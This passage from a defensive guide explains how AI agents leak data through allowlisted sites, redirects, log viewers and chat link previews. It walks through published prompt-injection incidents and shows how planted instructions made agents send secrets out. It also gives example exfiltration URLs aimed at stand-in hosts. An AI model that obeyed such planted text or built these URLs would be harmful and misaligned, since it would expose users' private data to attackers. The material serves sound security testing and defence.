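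Anthropic's rule for web_fetch, the tool its Claude models use to open web pages, is based on the conversation instead of an index. Willison quotes the documentation from September 2025, when Anthropic released the tool for developers. Claude could fetch an address that had appeared in the user's messages, in results from the developer's own tools, or in earlier search and fetch results, but not one it had composed itself. Willison tested this in the Claude app and found that the tool blocked composed addresses.

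He also noticed that many applications weaken this protection by pasting outside text, such as an email, into the user's message, which makes every link in that text a permitted address. In its documentation, Anthropic warned that some risk remained and advised developers not to use the tool where Claude handles untrusted text together with sensitive data.

### Spelling out data with permitted addresses

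Neither rule hides which permitted address the agent chose to open, so an attacker can still spell out a secret with fixed pages, as with pictures. If the attacker has N permitted pages and the agent opens k of them in order, the server's log can reveal up to

k × log₂ N bits

That's about 5.2 bits per request with 36 pages. This table shows the smallest number of requests that could carry some typical secrets:

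| Secret | Size | With 36 addresses | With 1,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bid below €1 million, to the euro | 19.9 bits | 4 requests | 2 requests |
| Any string of eight letters | 37.6 bits | 8 requests | 4 requests |
| 128-bit encryption key | 128 bits | 25 requests | 13 requests |

A model would need a fairly awkward encoding to reach some of these minimums. The obvious encoding, in which each page stands for one character, takes six requests to send the bid.

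Rehberger suggests storing each response for a few minutes, or refusing to open the same address twice in a session. Either measure would disrupt the obvious code, which uses one page for each digit from 0 to 9, because 412000 contains three zeros. But the rival could publish 60 pages, ten for each of the six digit positions. The agent would then open six different pages, and the rival could read the bid whatever order the requests arrived in. Capping the number of requests is a firmer limit, but an agent that reads 50 pages for a research task needs a high cap.

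In July 2026, Willison described how Ayush Paul had turned this weakness into an attack on the Claude app, which keeps memories of a user's earlier conversations. Paul used the part of the rule that permitted addresses from earlier fetch results. He built a site that gave Claude a pretext to look up the user by name, one letter at a time. Claude opened the link for the first letter, received a page with links for the second letter, and so on. Claude composed none of these addresses, so the tool allowed them all. The requests revealed the user's name, home city and employer to the site.

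Each choice among 26 letters can carry up to 4.7 bits, and Paul's site could generate new links for as long as Claude kept following them. To get around OpenAI's rule, an attacker has to get the pages into the crawler's index beforehand. The site also showed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person who checked the page wouldn't have seen them.

The rule itself was flawed, because an attacker's page could supply new permitted addresses. Anthropic removed the tool's ability to follow links from fetched pages, and said it had already found the problem internally. An attacker can no longer add permitted addresses during the conversation, but some choice of addresses remains. For instance, the attacker might get several pages into the search results. An application that pastes emails into the user's message has a bigger problem, because one email can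 contain all 36 links.

### FLOWSH: checking what a command has read

A rule about addresses can't tell whether a secret influenced the agent's choice. FLOWSH, which researchers mainly at Microsoft described in November 2026, looks instead at what the agent has read. It extends the labels of FIDES to shell commands, whose effects are hard to predict from their text. *Flowsh* describes the following procedure for network requests:

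1. FLOWSH starts each command in a sandbox, an isolated environment, and gives the command the label of the agent's context.
2. Whenever a program in the sandbox opens a file or connects to a site, FLOWSH combines the label of that source with the command's label, as FIDES does for the agent's context.
3. All network traffic goes to a proxy, a program that relays requests. Before it forwards one, FLOWSH pauses the command and adds the labels of any files read so far.
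4. The proxy forwards the request if everything behind it is trusted, or if the destination may read all the data. Otherwise it sends nothing and reports the blocked destination, so that the agent can ask the user to approve another attempt.

FLOWSH holds changes to files in a separate layer until the command ends and can then discard them, but it can't take back a request that a server has received.

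Suppose the rival's enquiry is in the context and Nadia's agent runs a command that downloads a public list of tile prices. FLOWSH allows this because the command has read nothing private. The agent then runs a second command that opens the bid spreadsheet and requests the same address. FLOWSH blocks this request because the context is untrusted and the site's owner may not read the bid. An allowlist would have to allow both requests or block both. The label check also stops the agent from spelling out the bid with 36 permitted pages, since it would have to open each page after reading the bid.

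The protection depends on correct labels. It also lets private data go to any site when everything the command has read is trusted, so it wouldn't prevent a leak caused by the agent's own mistake. A company can remove that exception, but this would lead to more requests for approval.

The researchers tested FLOWSH with OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Sol on 17 office tasks and 19 attacks, running each three times. Once planted text reached the model, they let the attacker dictate everything the model wrote. The reader-and-observer test is based on the same assumption. In one setting, nobody could approve anything. In the other, an ideal approver refused every action the attack had influenced and allowed the rest.

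| Defence | Successful attacks, no approver | Tasks completed, no approver | Tasks completed, ideal approver | Approvals per completed task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lax sandbox, which allows everything | 51 of 51 | 94.1% | 96.1% | 6.7 |
| Standard sandbox, with a list of common sites | 3 of 39 | 76.5% | 76.5% | 5.7 |
| Strict sandbox, with read-only files and only software package sites | 0 of 39 | 47.1% | 47.1% | 0 |
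| Labels that treat all shell output as private and untrusted | 0 of 32 | 35.3% | 60.8% | 1.8 |
| FLOWSH | 0 of 40 | 58.8% | 88.2% | 1.2 |

The number of attacks varies because the planted text didn't reach the model in every run. With the ideal approver, no attack succeeded under any defence, so the last column measures only how often each system had to ask for approval. Real approvers are less careful. *Flowsh* cites an Anthropic figure that users accept about 93% of the permission prompts in its programming tool, Claude Code. In 39 of 45 attack runs, FLOWSH's first question was about the attack, which should make the attack easier to notice. The researchers haven't tested whether people make better decisions as a result.

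The zero in the first column is weaker evidence about leaks than it seems. Eight of the 19 attacks were attempts to send data to the attacker's own server, and the other 11 were attempts to overwrite files. All three attacks that succeeded against the standard sandbox overwrote files, so its list of common sites also stopped every attempted leak. An attacker who collected the data through a listed site, such as GitHub, would have been a harder test.

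FLOWSH's advantage over the standard sandbox also depends on having someone to approve requests. Without an approver, it completed only 6 of the 27 runs that combined untrusted and private data, the combination that makes an agent worth attacking. Completed tasks took 17 to 34% longer than in the lax sandbox.

### What "this agent has no network" has to mean

In FLOWSH's sandbox, a shell's only network connection is loopback, which programs on the same machine use to communicate with each other. The shell can also reach the proxy through one socket, or connection point. The sandbox hides the machine's other sockets, including the one for Docker, a program that runs software in containers. If a command could reach Docker, it could start a container outside the sandbox and send the data from there. The proxy is therefore the only direct way for a command in the sandbox to contact another machine.

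For the whole agent to count as having no exfiltration sink among its tools, several more things must be true:

- Every tool must lack a route out, including those that run outside the sandbox. The agent in the FLOWSH tests had a separate web tool that didn't go through the shell. A document search that a supplier hosts also sends its queries over a network.
- The tools must not be able to look up outside names. A firewall may block web pages and still let the machine query a resolver.
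- No connected program may act on what the agent leaves behind. A Git hook, for example, is a small program that runs when a programmer next saves a version of some code, with the programmer's own network access. FLOWSH guards such files by letting only trusted commands change them.
- The company that runs the model must be in R. If the model isn't on the firm's own machines, its whole context travels to that company on every pass of the loop.

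Even then, the claim covers only the tools. The chat window can still load a picture.

To test it, the team can replace the model with a program that writes fixed tool calls, as in the earlier tests with canary URLs, and run everything where the tools normally run. The team should first make each attempt with the network connected, to confirm that the recording captures successful requests.

| Attempt | What would reveal a route out |
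|---|---|
| Put a canary URL in every text argument of every tool | A request at the canary server |
| Look up a unique name under the test domain | A query at the domain's name server |
| Connect to the canary server by its numerical address | A connection, even if no page loads |
| Send data over UDP, which many web filters ignore | A packet at the canary server |
| Install a package from the test server | A download request |
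| Try each local socket that the tools can see | A reply from a program with network access |
| Write a canary request into files that other programs run, then use the machine normally | A request hours or days later |

Data can leave the network even when the tool reports an error. "Page could not be loaded" can appear after a successful name lookup, or after the server has received the address and returned nothing. To check whether any data left, the team needs the records of the canary server and its name server, and a recording of all traffic at the edge of its own network.

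A customer can't record the supplier's traffic for a hosted product such as Rovo. An administrator can still turn web search off, ask the agent to open a canary URL directly, and watch that URL's server for a request. A request would show that the agent still has a tool that can reach the web. If none arrives, the agent may have declined to try, so the administrator should also ask the supplier which tools the model still has when web search is off.

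## Approved destinations that an outsider can read

Most agents need some network access, so teams often restrict them to an allowlist of approved destinations. This stops many leaks, but teams often wrongly conclude that it stops all of them. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an internal exercise in which a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt full of routine setup steps. One step was to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server, and Claude Code did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the user had supplied the instruction, a classifier had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the agent's file and network access would have stopped the leak.

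But an allowlist names machines, and a leak depends on who can read what those machines receive. For an approved destination a, the direct observers are

direct(a) = owner(a) ∪ accounts(a)

Here owner(a) is whoever controls the site and can read its logs, and accounts(a) is everyone who can use their own account or page on the site to collect what the agent sends. As with any consumer, Obs(a) also includes the observers of anything the site forwards requests to. Every entry on the allowlist has to pass the reader-and-observer test, even if the site is reputable.

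### A trusted name that had expired

A year before SalesBleed, the security company Noma reported another leak from Salesforce's Agentforce, called ForcedLeak. *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025) describes how it also began with a public form for sales enquiries. Most of the form's fields hold 40 to 80 characters, but the description field holds 42,000, more than enough for planted instructions. When an employee asked the agent to deal with the enquiry, it collected the email addresses of other potential customers and put them in an image's URL.

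The page's CSP allowed pictures from only 22 site names and patterns. One of them covered `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had lapsed. Noma bought it for $5 and became the overlooked observer. The employee's browser then sent the addresses to Noma's server, as the CSP permitted.

Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025. Salesforce regained the domain and, according to The Hacker News (2025), released patches that stop agents from sending output to any address not on a list of Trusted URLs. Enforcement began on September 8. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* notes that administrators had to list every external domain their agents needed or risk disruption. SalesBleed later evaded this check with oddly formed addresses.

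Buying back the expired domain alone would probably not have been enough. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces Noma's report with the full CSP, which also allowed images from `*.amazonaws.com` and `*.cloudinary.com`. Amazon and Cloudinary host files for anyone who opens an account. An attacker who could see the requests for their own hosted files would not have needed the expired domain.

### A trusted site with forms that anyone can create

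Superhuman, an email app with an AI assistant, allowed pictures from `docs.google.com`. Google owned the domain and still does, but it also hosts Google Forms there, and anyone can create a form and read the replies. A form's creator can also write a link that fills in an answer and submits it as soon as someone opens the link. For the roofing bid, the link would look roughly like this:

```
https://docs.google.com/forms/d/e/FORM-ID/formResponse?entry.1=412000
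```

In PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, a user asks for a summary of recent mail, and one message contains a planted instruction. The assistant puts the text of other emails into a link that submits a Google Form, then displays the link as an image. When the browser tries to load the image, Google Forms records the text as a response, and the attacker reads it. Willison (2026), in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, traces the leak to the combination of a content security policy (CSP) entry that allows requests to Google Forms and a form that stores data from an ordinary page request.

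One answer could carry the full text of several emails, or parts of more than 40. PromptArmor reported the flaw on a Friday night in December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday, deployed its first patch on Tuesday, and released further patches up to January 11, 2026.

A few months later, Google Forms was again the sink. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes how a planted email made OpenAI's Codex, a programming agent that had just gained office features, send a user's emails to a form in the same way. OpenAI fixed this after a report in April 2026. OpenAI's Safe Url rule for ChatGPT would have blocked such an address, so Codex's display presumably didn't apply it.

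Administrators can easily add the same weakness. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of an address to trust, so that the agent can show links to a company's own documents. PromptArmor advises Salesforce customers to block images from a trusted site unless they need them. That would stop the automatic request, but a person who clicked the link would still submit the form.

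### One address, many accounts

Claude Cowork is Anthropic's agent for office work on a user's own computer. It runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that can access only the folders the user selects and the sites on an approved list. One approved site was `api.anthropic.com`, which Cowork needs to work.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published two days after Cowork's release in January 2026, describes an attack in which a user gives Cowork a folder of property documents and a file with hidden instructions. The file also contains the attacker's API key, a code that identifies the customer making a request to Anthropic's servers. Claude uses that key to upload the largest document to the attacker's Anthropic account, without asking for approval. PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, a small model, but Claude Opus 4.5 leaked customer records by the same route in another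 test.

Anthropic runs the model and already sees the user's data, so a team could reasonably have put Anthropic in R and approved the address on that basis. The overlooked consumer was Anthropic's file service, which delivers each upload to the account whose key came with it. The document therefore went to an account whose owner, unlike Anthropic, wasn't authorised to read it.

Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* had described this route in October 2025, in Claude's feature for running code. The default setting was called "Package managers only", but the first entry on its list of approved destinations was `api.anthropic.com`. A single upload could carry 30 megabytes. Anthropic closed the report as out of scope within an hour, but acknowledged five days later that it should have accepted it.

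Anthropic later wrote that the sandbox had "worked perfectly" and the data had still got out. It now regards an allowlist entry as a "capability grant", meaning that approving a site also approves everything a request to that site can do. Its fix was a proxy inside the virtual machine that accepts only requests that carry the machine's own session token, so it rejects any that use an attacker's key. The proxy also blocks headers (extra fields in a request) that would make Anthropic's server fetch an address. Anthropic put this check on the user's side because its servers can't tell a Cowork request from any other customer's.

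### A site built to show requests

Antigravity, Google's programming tool, includes an agent that can open pages in a browser. In November 2025, PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* demonstrated an attack that used a web guide containing instructions in tiny type. Antigravity collected code and passwords from the user's project, then opened a `webhook.site` URL that included the data.

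Anyone can create an address on webhook.site and see the requests sent to it. Programmers use such sites to check what their own software sends, which is presumably why the default allowlist for Antigravity's browser included this one. Whoever compiled the list overlooked that the person who created an address can read what the agent sends there. Other approved sites become sinks through a side feature, whereas displaying incoming requests is webhook.site's main purpose.

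Google responded by warning users about data exfiltration when they first open the program. PromptArmor did not report the flaw privately because Google had indicated that it already knew of such risks. Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* describes the default list as optional and explains that when the browser reaches an unlisted site, the user sees an "always allow" button that adds the site permanently. A user can therefore add a site to a carefully reviewed list with one click.

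An organisation can restrict Antigravity's browser to its own list of approved destinations, but this setting applies only to the browser agent and blocks nothing by default, according to Google Cloud's *Configure AI developer tools settings*. Antigravity can also run terminal commands and display pictures in the chat, and *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) describes a leak that combined the two.

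### Redirects

A redirect is a reply from a server that sends the visitor on to another address. Suppose the roofing firm approves its tile supplier's site, which has a page for outgoing links:

```
https://tiles.example/go?to=https://rival.example/412000
```

The agent's tool checks the address, finds the supplier's name and makes the request. The supplier's server replies with a redirect, and the tool follows it to the rival. OpenAI gives this as one reason not to rely on lists of trusted sites, since many legitimate sites support redirects and a check may look only at the first domain.

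A browser that enforces a CSP checks the site's name again after each redirect, so it would block a picture that ended up at rival.example. But W3C's standard contains an exception that matters for companies trying to approve only part of a site. Suppose the firm's policy is:

```
img-src tiles.example docs.google.com/document/
```

The browser blocks a direct request for a Google form, because its path begins with `/forms/`. If tiles.example redirects the browser to the form, the request goes through, because the browser ignores the path after a redirect. W3C chose this deliberately, because otherwise a malicious page could try one path after another in its own policy to find out where another site had redirected the visitor.

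Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) describes a stricter mechanism, which checks every connection from a page, including redirects, against a list of address patterns. Google scheduled the trial for Chrome versions 148 to 151. However, a pattern can still permit other people's accounts on an approved site. The example in Google's article, `https://api.example.com/*`, permits any path on the site, and a similar pattern for docs.google.com would permit every form, whoever owns it.

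None of these checks covers an approved site that fetches an address itself, as Bing did in SearchLeak, because the approved server then sends the next request.

### What to ask about each entry

A team can fill in Obs(a) by asking the same questions about every entry:

| Question | Where it mattered | How to find out |
|---|---|---|
| Who owns the name, and when does the registration end? | ForcedLeak | Public registration record |
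| Can strangers open accounts or create pages there? | Superhuman, Cowork, Antigravity | Sign up as an outsider |
| Does the site store or display what a request contains, and to whom? | Superhuman, Cowork, Antigravity | Send a unique word and look for it from the outsider's account |
| Does the site fetch addresses that it receives? | EchoLeak, SearchLeak | Give it a canary URL |
| Does it redirect visitors to addresses that others can choose? | The supplier's link page | Ask it to redirect to a canary URL |

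For an entry with an asterisk, the answers have to hold for every site under that name. The site's owner matters even when the site has no accounts. The tile supplier, Lars's employer, can read its own logs and isn't allowed to know the bid, so its site fails the test even without a link page.

Domain ownership needs rechecking, because an entry can become dangerous without anyone editing the list. The domain used in ForcedLeak would have passed a review on any day before its registration lapsed. A calendar reminder helps with domains the company owns. For other people's domains, it's safer to delete entries that the agent no longer uses.

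### Narrower rules and what they cost

Few popular sites pass all these questions. A company can still use one if it restricts what the agent may send there.

The list can contain **exact addresses**, including everything after the question mark, instead of site names. This would have stopped the leaks in ForcedLeak, Superhuman and Antigravity, because each attack needed an address with private data in it. It also limits the harm if a listed domain expires, because the new owner receives only requests for addresses already on the list, although they could reply with planted instructions. The tool has to check the address again after every redirect, and the agent can still leak a secret through its choice of permitted addresses.

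Restricting requests to an exact address wouldn't have stopped the Cowork leak, because every customer uploads files to the same address and the document is sent in the body of the request. The rule therefore also has to cover the body and headers, for example by allowing only plain page requests with no content from the model.

Somebody has to approve every new page, so the agent can't run a search or follow a link that nobody anticipated. The rule suits an agent that consults the same ten pages every day, but it is nearly useless for research. Detailed lists also break when a site reorganises its pages. W3C calls exhaustive lists of resources "brittle, awkward, and difficult to implement and maintain".

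**Fixed accounts.** A proxy can require every request to a service to use the company's own account, as Anthropic's does. Embrace The Red proposed this in its original report. It prevents the agent from uploading to a stranger's account without limiting which documents it may upload, so the agent stays useful.

But the proxy has to read encrypted traffic and detect how each service identifies its customers. Embrace The Red warned that other sites on Claude's default list might allow similar leaks, and that list included GitHub, where anyone can open an account. Each such service needs its own check. The rule doesn't work for Google Forms or webhook.site, which accept data from visitors who have no account. It also doesn't control what happens inside the right account, where an agent might create a public sharing link for a private file, so the account should not have permission to share.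 Someone who legitimately has two accounts with a service can use only one through the agent.

The company can have ordinary code write the requests instead of the model. Suppose the roofing firm replaces the general web tool with one that looks up tile prices. The model chooses one of 200 products, and the code builds the address. The model can no longer put the bid directly into the address, but it can still encode the bid in the sequence of products it looks up, since two lookups allow 40,000 sequences.

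A program that downloads the supplier's whole price list every night removes that channel too. The agent reads the copy on the firm's own server. Nothing in the agent's context affects whether, when or how the program makes its request, so the supplier learns nothing about the bid from it. However, the prices may be a day old, and Nadia can't ask about a supplier whose list the firm doesn't download.

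To test the allowlist, the team should set up an account, form or request log at each approved service, as an outsider would, and have the fixed-text program send a unique word there. If the word arrives where an outsider can read it, that allowlist entry is an exfiltration sink. Canary URLs on the team's own domain can't test these entries, because the allowlist blocks that domain.

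## Log viewers, chat apps and mail programs run by other parties

An allowlist limits what the agent's own machine can contact. It doesn't restrict a chat company's servers that receive the agent's answer, or a web page where the model's provider shows old answers to developers, because these consumers have their own network access. The company that deploys the agent didn't write them and often can't configure them, so they are the hardest consumers to rule out as sinks.

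### The log page that displayed a blocked answer

When a company uses OpenAI's models through the API, OpenAI stores the responses by default, and the company's developers can read them on a log page on OpenAI's website. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes how this page could leak an answer that the company's software had blocked.

The researchers built a mock version of the tools banks use to check customers' identities. These tools check private details against web material, so they handle both together.

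1. The tool gathered six sources about a customer. One contained text from the web in which an attacker had planted an instruction.
2. A user chose one of the tool's suggested questions. The model followed the planted instruction and wrote a Markdown picture whose address, on the attacker's server, included the customer's details.
3. A second model, which the tool used to judge answers, flagged this one. The tool blocked it, and no data left.
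4. A developer opened the flagged conversation on OpenAI's log page to see what had gone wrong.
5. The log page interpreted the stored answer as Markdown, so the developer's browser requested the picture. The attacker's server log then contained the customer's passport details, social security number and credit history.

A team listing the tool's consumers could easily leave out the log page, since it belongs to the model's supplier and customers never see it. A better sanitiser in the tool wouldn't have helped, because OpenAI keeps its own copy of the model's output and the tool can clean only the copy it receives. PromptArmor notes that a content security policy (CSP), an image filter or a plain-text display would also protect the tool's users but leave the log page exposed. FIDES's assumption that attackers cannot observe the model's responses also fails here.

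These other defences raise no alarm, so a developer needs some other reason to open that particular record, such as a user's complaint. PromptArmor shows an answer from the search service Perplexity after a filter had removed a Markdown image. The remaining text was odd and empty, and a user might reasonably click "thumbs down" on it. If the company reviews answers with bad ratings, the filter in effect leads a developer to open the one dangerous record among thousands.

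The attack is slower and less certain than a leak through a chat window, because somebody also has to read the log. PromptArmor has no figures on how often that happens. But the attacker loses nothing by waiting, and developers look at flagged conversations as a normal part of their job.

PromptArmor reported the problem on November 17, 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. It then sent four follow-ups with instructions for reproducing the leak and answers to questions. The report was closed as "not applicable" on December 4 without OpenAI having seen it. OpenAI learned of the problem from PromptArmor's published article, confirmed it, and reopened the report on January 22, 2026. In July 2026, PromptArmor's article still described a fix as under way, and apparently no one has publicly confirmed since then that the fix is finished. Until a company has tested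 the affected page with its own account, it should assume that the page still loads pictures.

PromptArmor found the same flaw in the preview windows where developers test an agent and in a starter app that OpenAI gives them to build on. Companies that copied the starter app can fix their own copies, but only OpenAI can fix the preview windows and the log page.

### Keeping answers out of the log

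A deployer can keep answers off the log page by not storing them. According to OpenAI's *Your data*, OpenAI keeps responses for at least 30 days by default, and conversations (longer exchanges saved on its servers) until someone deletes them. A developer can add `store: false` to a request for a response. In *Does store*, on OpenAI's developer forum, dev_99230421 asked whether administrators could still read such a request in the logs. The reply was that the request doesn't appear there, although its cost appears on the usage page.

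Requests should set `store` explicitly. In *Chat completions always stored*, a developer reports that requests that omitted `store` appeared in the logs, contrary to the documented default. Large companies can apply to OpenAI for Zero Data Retention, which treats `store` as false even if a request sets it to true. This helps when a programmer forgets the setting, but it doesn't cover saved conversations.

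A reply in *How to disable Response API logs* mentions another setting, which controls who in the organisation can see the logs, but recommends `store: false` instead. Restricting access reduces the number of people who could trigger the leak, but anyone who still has access could trigger it.

Turning storage off removes a useful debugging tool. A company that still wants records can keep them on its own server and display them as plain text. If it has to use OpenAI's page, reviewers can open the page in a browser that blocks pictures from unknown sites. This works because the reviewer's own machine sends the request for each picture.

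### Link previews

When someone posts a link in a chat app, the app often shows the page's title and a picture below it. To get these, the chat company's server fetches the page, a step that Slack calls unfurling. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, the company's servers must fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to.

Suppose the roofing firm's agent posts its answers in a private Slack channel whose only members are Nadia and Ewa, the two people allowed to read both the bid and the supplier's email. The firm has decided that Slack, as its supplier, may see the bid too. If u₁ to uₙ are the addresses in a message, the observers are

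Obs(channel) = members ∪ {Slack} ∪ owner(u₁) ∪ … ∪ owner(uₙ)

An attacker who controls the text also chooses the addresses in it, so the recipients can include anyone. If the model writes `https://rival.example/?n=412000`, Slack's server requests the page, and the rival receives the bid before Nadia opens the channel. The agent itself contacts only Slack, which is probably on its allowlist.

Johann Rehberger described this leak in Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* in August 2024. He posted a link through a Slack app and found a request from "Slackbot-LinkExpanding" in his own server's log. Willison (2024), who had been collecting such leaks for over a year, wrote that he hadn't thought of this one before. The remedy is to add two settings to each message:

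```
"unfurl_links": false,
"unfurl_media": false
```

The first covers pages that are mostly text, and the second covers pictures, video and sound. A developer needs both, because the attacker decides what the linked server returns.

### A connector limited to one private channel

Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* shows how easily a careful deployer can miss this. Anthropic had published a connector for posting to Slack through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of giving tools to agents. A company that restricts the connector to a single private channel might reasonably let the agent post without approval, expecting only that channel's members to see the posts.

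In one demonstration, a programmer asks Claude Code to analyse a file that contains invisible instructions. The agent reads a secret key from the programmer's project and posts a link containing the key in Slack, which then fetches the link. If the link leads to a picture, three separate Slack programs request it, so the key leaks several times.

Rehberger reported the flaw on May 27, 2025. Two days later, Anthropic archived the connector and said it would not maintain it. It's unclear whether the report prompted the archiving. People were still downloading the connector more than 14,000 times a week when Rehberger published the advisory. Because Anthropic doesn't maintain it, each company that uses it has to add the two lines itself or switch to a maintained connector.

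### The OpenClaw and Telegram test

OpenClaw is an agent that people talk to through messaging apps. In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reported that OpenClaw's default setup for Telegram leaked data through link previews. PromptArmor also opened a site where anyone could test their own combination of agent and app. The user got the agent to write a link to the site, which displayed any preview request it received, including the data and the name of the program that sent it. One logged request contained a name and an API key.

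OpenClaw users can stop this leak by adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the configuration file. In a repeat of the test with that setting, no data reached the site.

The results show that the vulnerability depends on both the agent and the app that displays its output. The same agent can be safe in a terminal and leak in Telegram, so a security review of the agent alone would miss the problem. Because volunteers chose what to test, the results can't be used to estimate what share of agents leak.

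### Copilot Cowork: messages to the user's own account

Microsoft's agent Copilot Cowork, which could leak download links through emails to its own user, works with an employee's files, mail and chats. Microsoft promises in its documentation that Cowork asks permission before sensitive actions such as sending an email or posting in Teams, its chat app. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, published in May 2026, found that Cowork sent emails and Teams messages to the employee using it without asking permission, and that employees had no setting to change this.

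The exception makes sense if nobody but the recipient can learn anything from a message. In PromptArmor's demonstration, an employee had uploaded a skill (a file of instructions for a kind of task) found online. Five of its 81 lines were malicious. When the employee asked for a summary of the week's work, Cowork collected download links for recent files and sent the employee a Teams message containing HTML picture tags, with the links in the pictures' addresses. Opening the message in Teams triggered requests to those addresses. Opening an email in Outlook, Microsoft's mail program, could do the same.

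Anyone who has one of these download links can use it without signing in. The attacker therefore needed only a few hundred characters in a picture's address to get an entire file, so limiting the length of addresses would have done little to prevent the leak.

The employee had little chance to notice the leak, because Cowork's record of the finished task showed that it had sent a Teams message but not what the message contained. The attack succeeded in all five trials. With so few trials, the true success rate could be much lower, since a rate of 55% would still produce five successes about 5% of the time (0.55⁵ ≈ 0.05), but even that rate would be enough for an attacker. Claude Opus 4.7, a stronger model than the one Cowork chose automatically, searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. Employees can also schedule a summary to run automatically every week, which would repeat the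 leak each time.

An administrator can't turn the exception off but can reduce what the attacker gets. SharePoint, where the files are stored, has a setting that blocks downloads, either for a whole site or for files with a chosen sensitivity label. People can then read those files only in a browser and can't print them or open them in Word or Excel. Few companies would accept that for all their documents, so applying the setting by label is more practical.

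### Cleaning the output or fixing the consumer

A deployer has good reasons to clean an agent's output before sending it to another party's program. The deployer often can't see what that program does with the text or where the text goes next. Cleaning the output first covers every program that receives it, including any connected later. It also doesn't require waiting for another company to fix its software, which matters when a supplier closes a vulnerability report without reading it or abandons a connector that thousands of people use.

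The sender has to guess which parts of the text are dangerous. OpenAI's log page loaded Markdown pictures, Slack fetches plain web addresses, and Teams loaded HTML picture tags. A filter that removes Markdown pictures misses the other two. Only text with no addresses is safe from automatic requests in all three, but a research agent isn't much use if it can't link to what it found. Even a filter that removed every address would act too late for the log page.

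The company that makes the receiving program knows exactly what that program interprets, and can protect every sender with one change. For displays of model output, PromptArmor recommends a strong CSP and loading external images only after the user has seen the full address and approved it. Developers using OpenAI's log page would lose almost nothing from this, because they go there to find out what the model wrote, and they can see that better in raw text than in a formatted version.

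For chat apps, the case for changing only the consumer is weaker, because colleagues like to see previews of each other's links and Slack has no way to distinguish a confidential bid from an order number in an address. Whoever sets up the sending program knows that a model writes its messages, and can use the two unfurling settings to turn previews off. PromptArmor likewise says that chat companies should offer a setting, and that agent developers should use it or pass the choice to their users. It would also like chat companies to let people turn previews off for a whole channel, so that protection doesn't depend on every program that posts there.

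Slack advises developers in its documentation to consider disabling previews for messages from a language model, but previews are on by default and stay on for anyone who hasn't read the advice. An agent framework that posts to chat apps should probably turn them off automatically.

In Copilot Cowork's case, Microsoft makes the agent as well as Teams and Outlook, so it could have closed the leak at either end.

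| Incident | Who requests the attacker's address | What the deployer can do | What the supplier can do |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's log page | The reviewer's browser | Set `store` to false; read logs as plain text elsewhere | OpenAI can stop the page loading outside pictures |
| Anthropic's Slack connector | Slack's servers | Add the two settings or replace the connector | Slack can change the default; Anthropic no longer maintains the connector |
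| OpenClaw in Telegram | Telegram's servers | Set `linkPreview` to false | OpenClaw can change its default |
| Copilot Cowork | The employee's Teams or Outlook, on opening the message | Block downloads of sensitive files; restrict skills from outside | Microsoft can require approval or stop loading outside pictures |

### What to do about a consumer that nobody can inspect

Testers can use the fixed text and canary URLs described earlier here too, but the form of the link matters. Slack doesn't unfurl an address without `http://` or `https://`, or a link whose visible label is part of its own address. A tester who used one of these forms might see no request and wrongly conclude that the channel was safe. A missing preview doesn't show that Slack made no request, because Slack fetches an address before it decides whether to display a preview. The tester has to check the canary server's log.

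**Turning features off** is the best remedy where a setting exists, because it works whatever the model writes. But it applies only to the deployer's own messages. If Nadia copies the agent's link into another channel, Slack treats her post as an ordinary message from a person and fetches the address.

The supplier should commit in writing that the product displays model output as text, that neither the product nor the supplier's servers request any address in that output, and that it will give notice before changing this. A general promise to keep data secure doesn't cover these points. The commitment should apply to phone apps and administrators' pages as well as the main product.

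A supplier's commitment still needs testing, because suppliers' descriptions of their own products can be wrong. Microsoft's account of Cowork's approvals left out messages to the user, and OpenAI's stated default for storage didn't match what one developer saw. Slack says on one page that it unfurls all links in messages from apps by default, but later on that page gives an example of an app's text link that will not unfurl unless the developer asks for it.

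The roofing firm could send less to Slack by keeping the answer on its own server and having ordinary code post a fixed sentence, such as "Your tile comparison is ready", with a link to a page that requires a login. Slack would fetch only the login page, which contains nothing about the bid. The model writes none of the message, so an attacker can't add an address to it. Nadia has to click once more to read her answer, and her colleagues can't discuss it directly below the post.

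If none of this gives an answer, the team can treat the consumer as a sink and replace "unknown" in its list with "everyone". The consumer then passes the reader-and-observer test only for outputs based entirely on public data. Any other output needs a sanitiser that removes every address, in whatever form. The sanitiser deals only with automatic requests, so the supplier's staff and anyone else who can read the text must still be in R.

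The broadband company has no better option for its customers' mail programs, because it can't test them all or change their settings, and customers never promised it anything. Plain-text email without model-written links would prevent most automatic requests, but a customer who isn't entitled to the data could still read it in the message.

### Sinks that arrive with an update

A supplier can turn a safe consumer into a sink without any change to the deployer's code, prompts or permissions. In *New "Chat Completions Logs" feature in API Platform*, a developer describes finding a new log page that had arrived with OpenAI's Responses API. The developer was pleased because the page would help to trace errors, and expressed no concern about how it would display a malicious answer, a question PromptArmor raised later.

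An update can also add observers to a feature that people already use. Slack lets an app register up to five web domains and receive the links to them that people post. *App unfurls everywhere* (Slack, 2020) announced that apps with the newer type of permissions would probably receive more links, and might display more previews, without their developers doing anything. Free teams got the change first and paying teams got it gradually afterwards, so two companies with identical settings could have had different observers in the same week. Slack's current documentation suggests that apps don't receive links posted by other apps. If so, they wouldn't receive a link from the agent's own message, but they would if a colleague reposted it.

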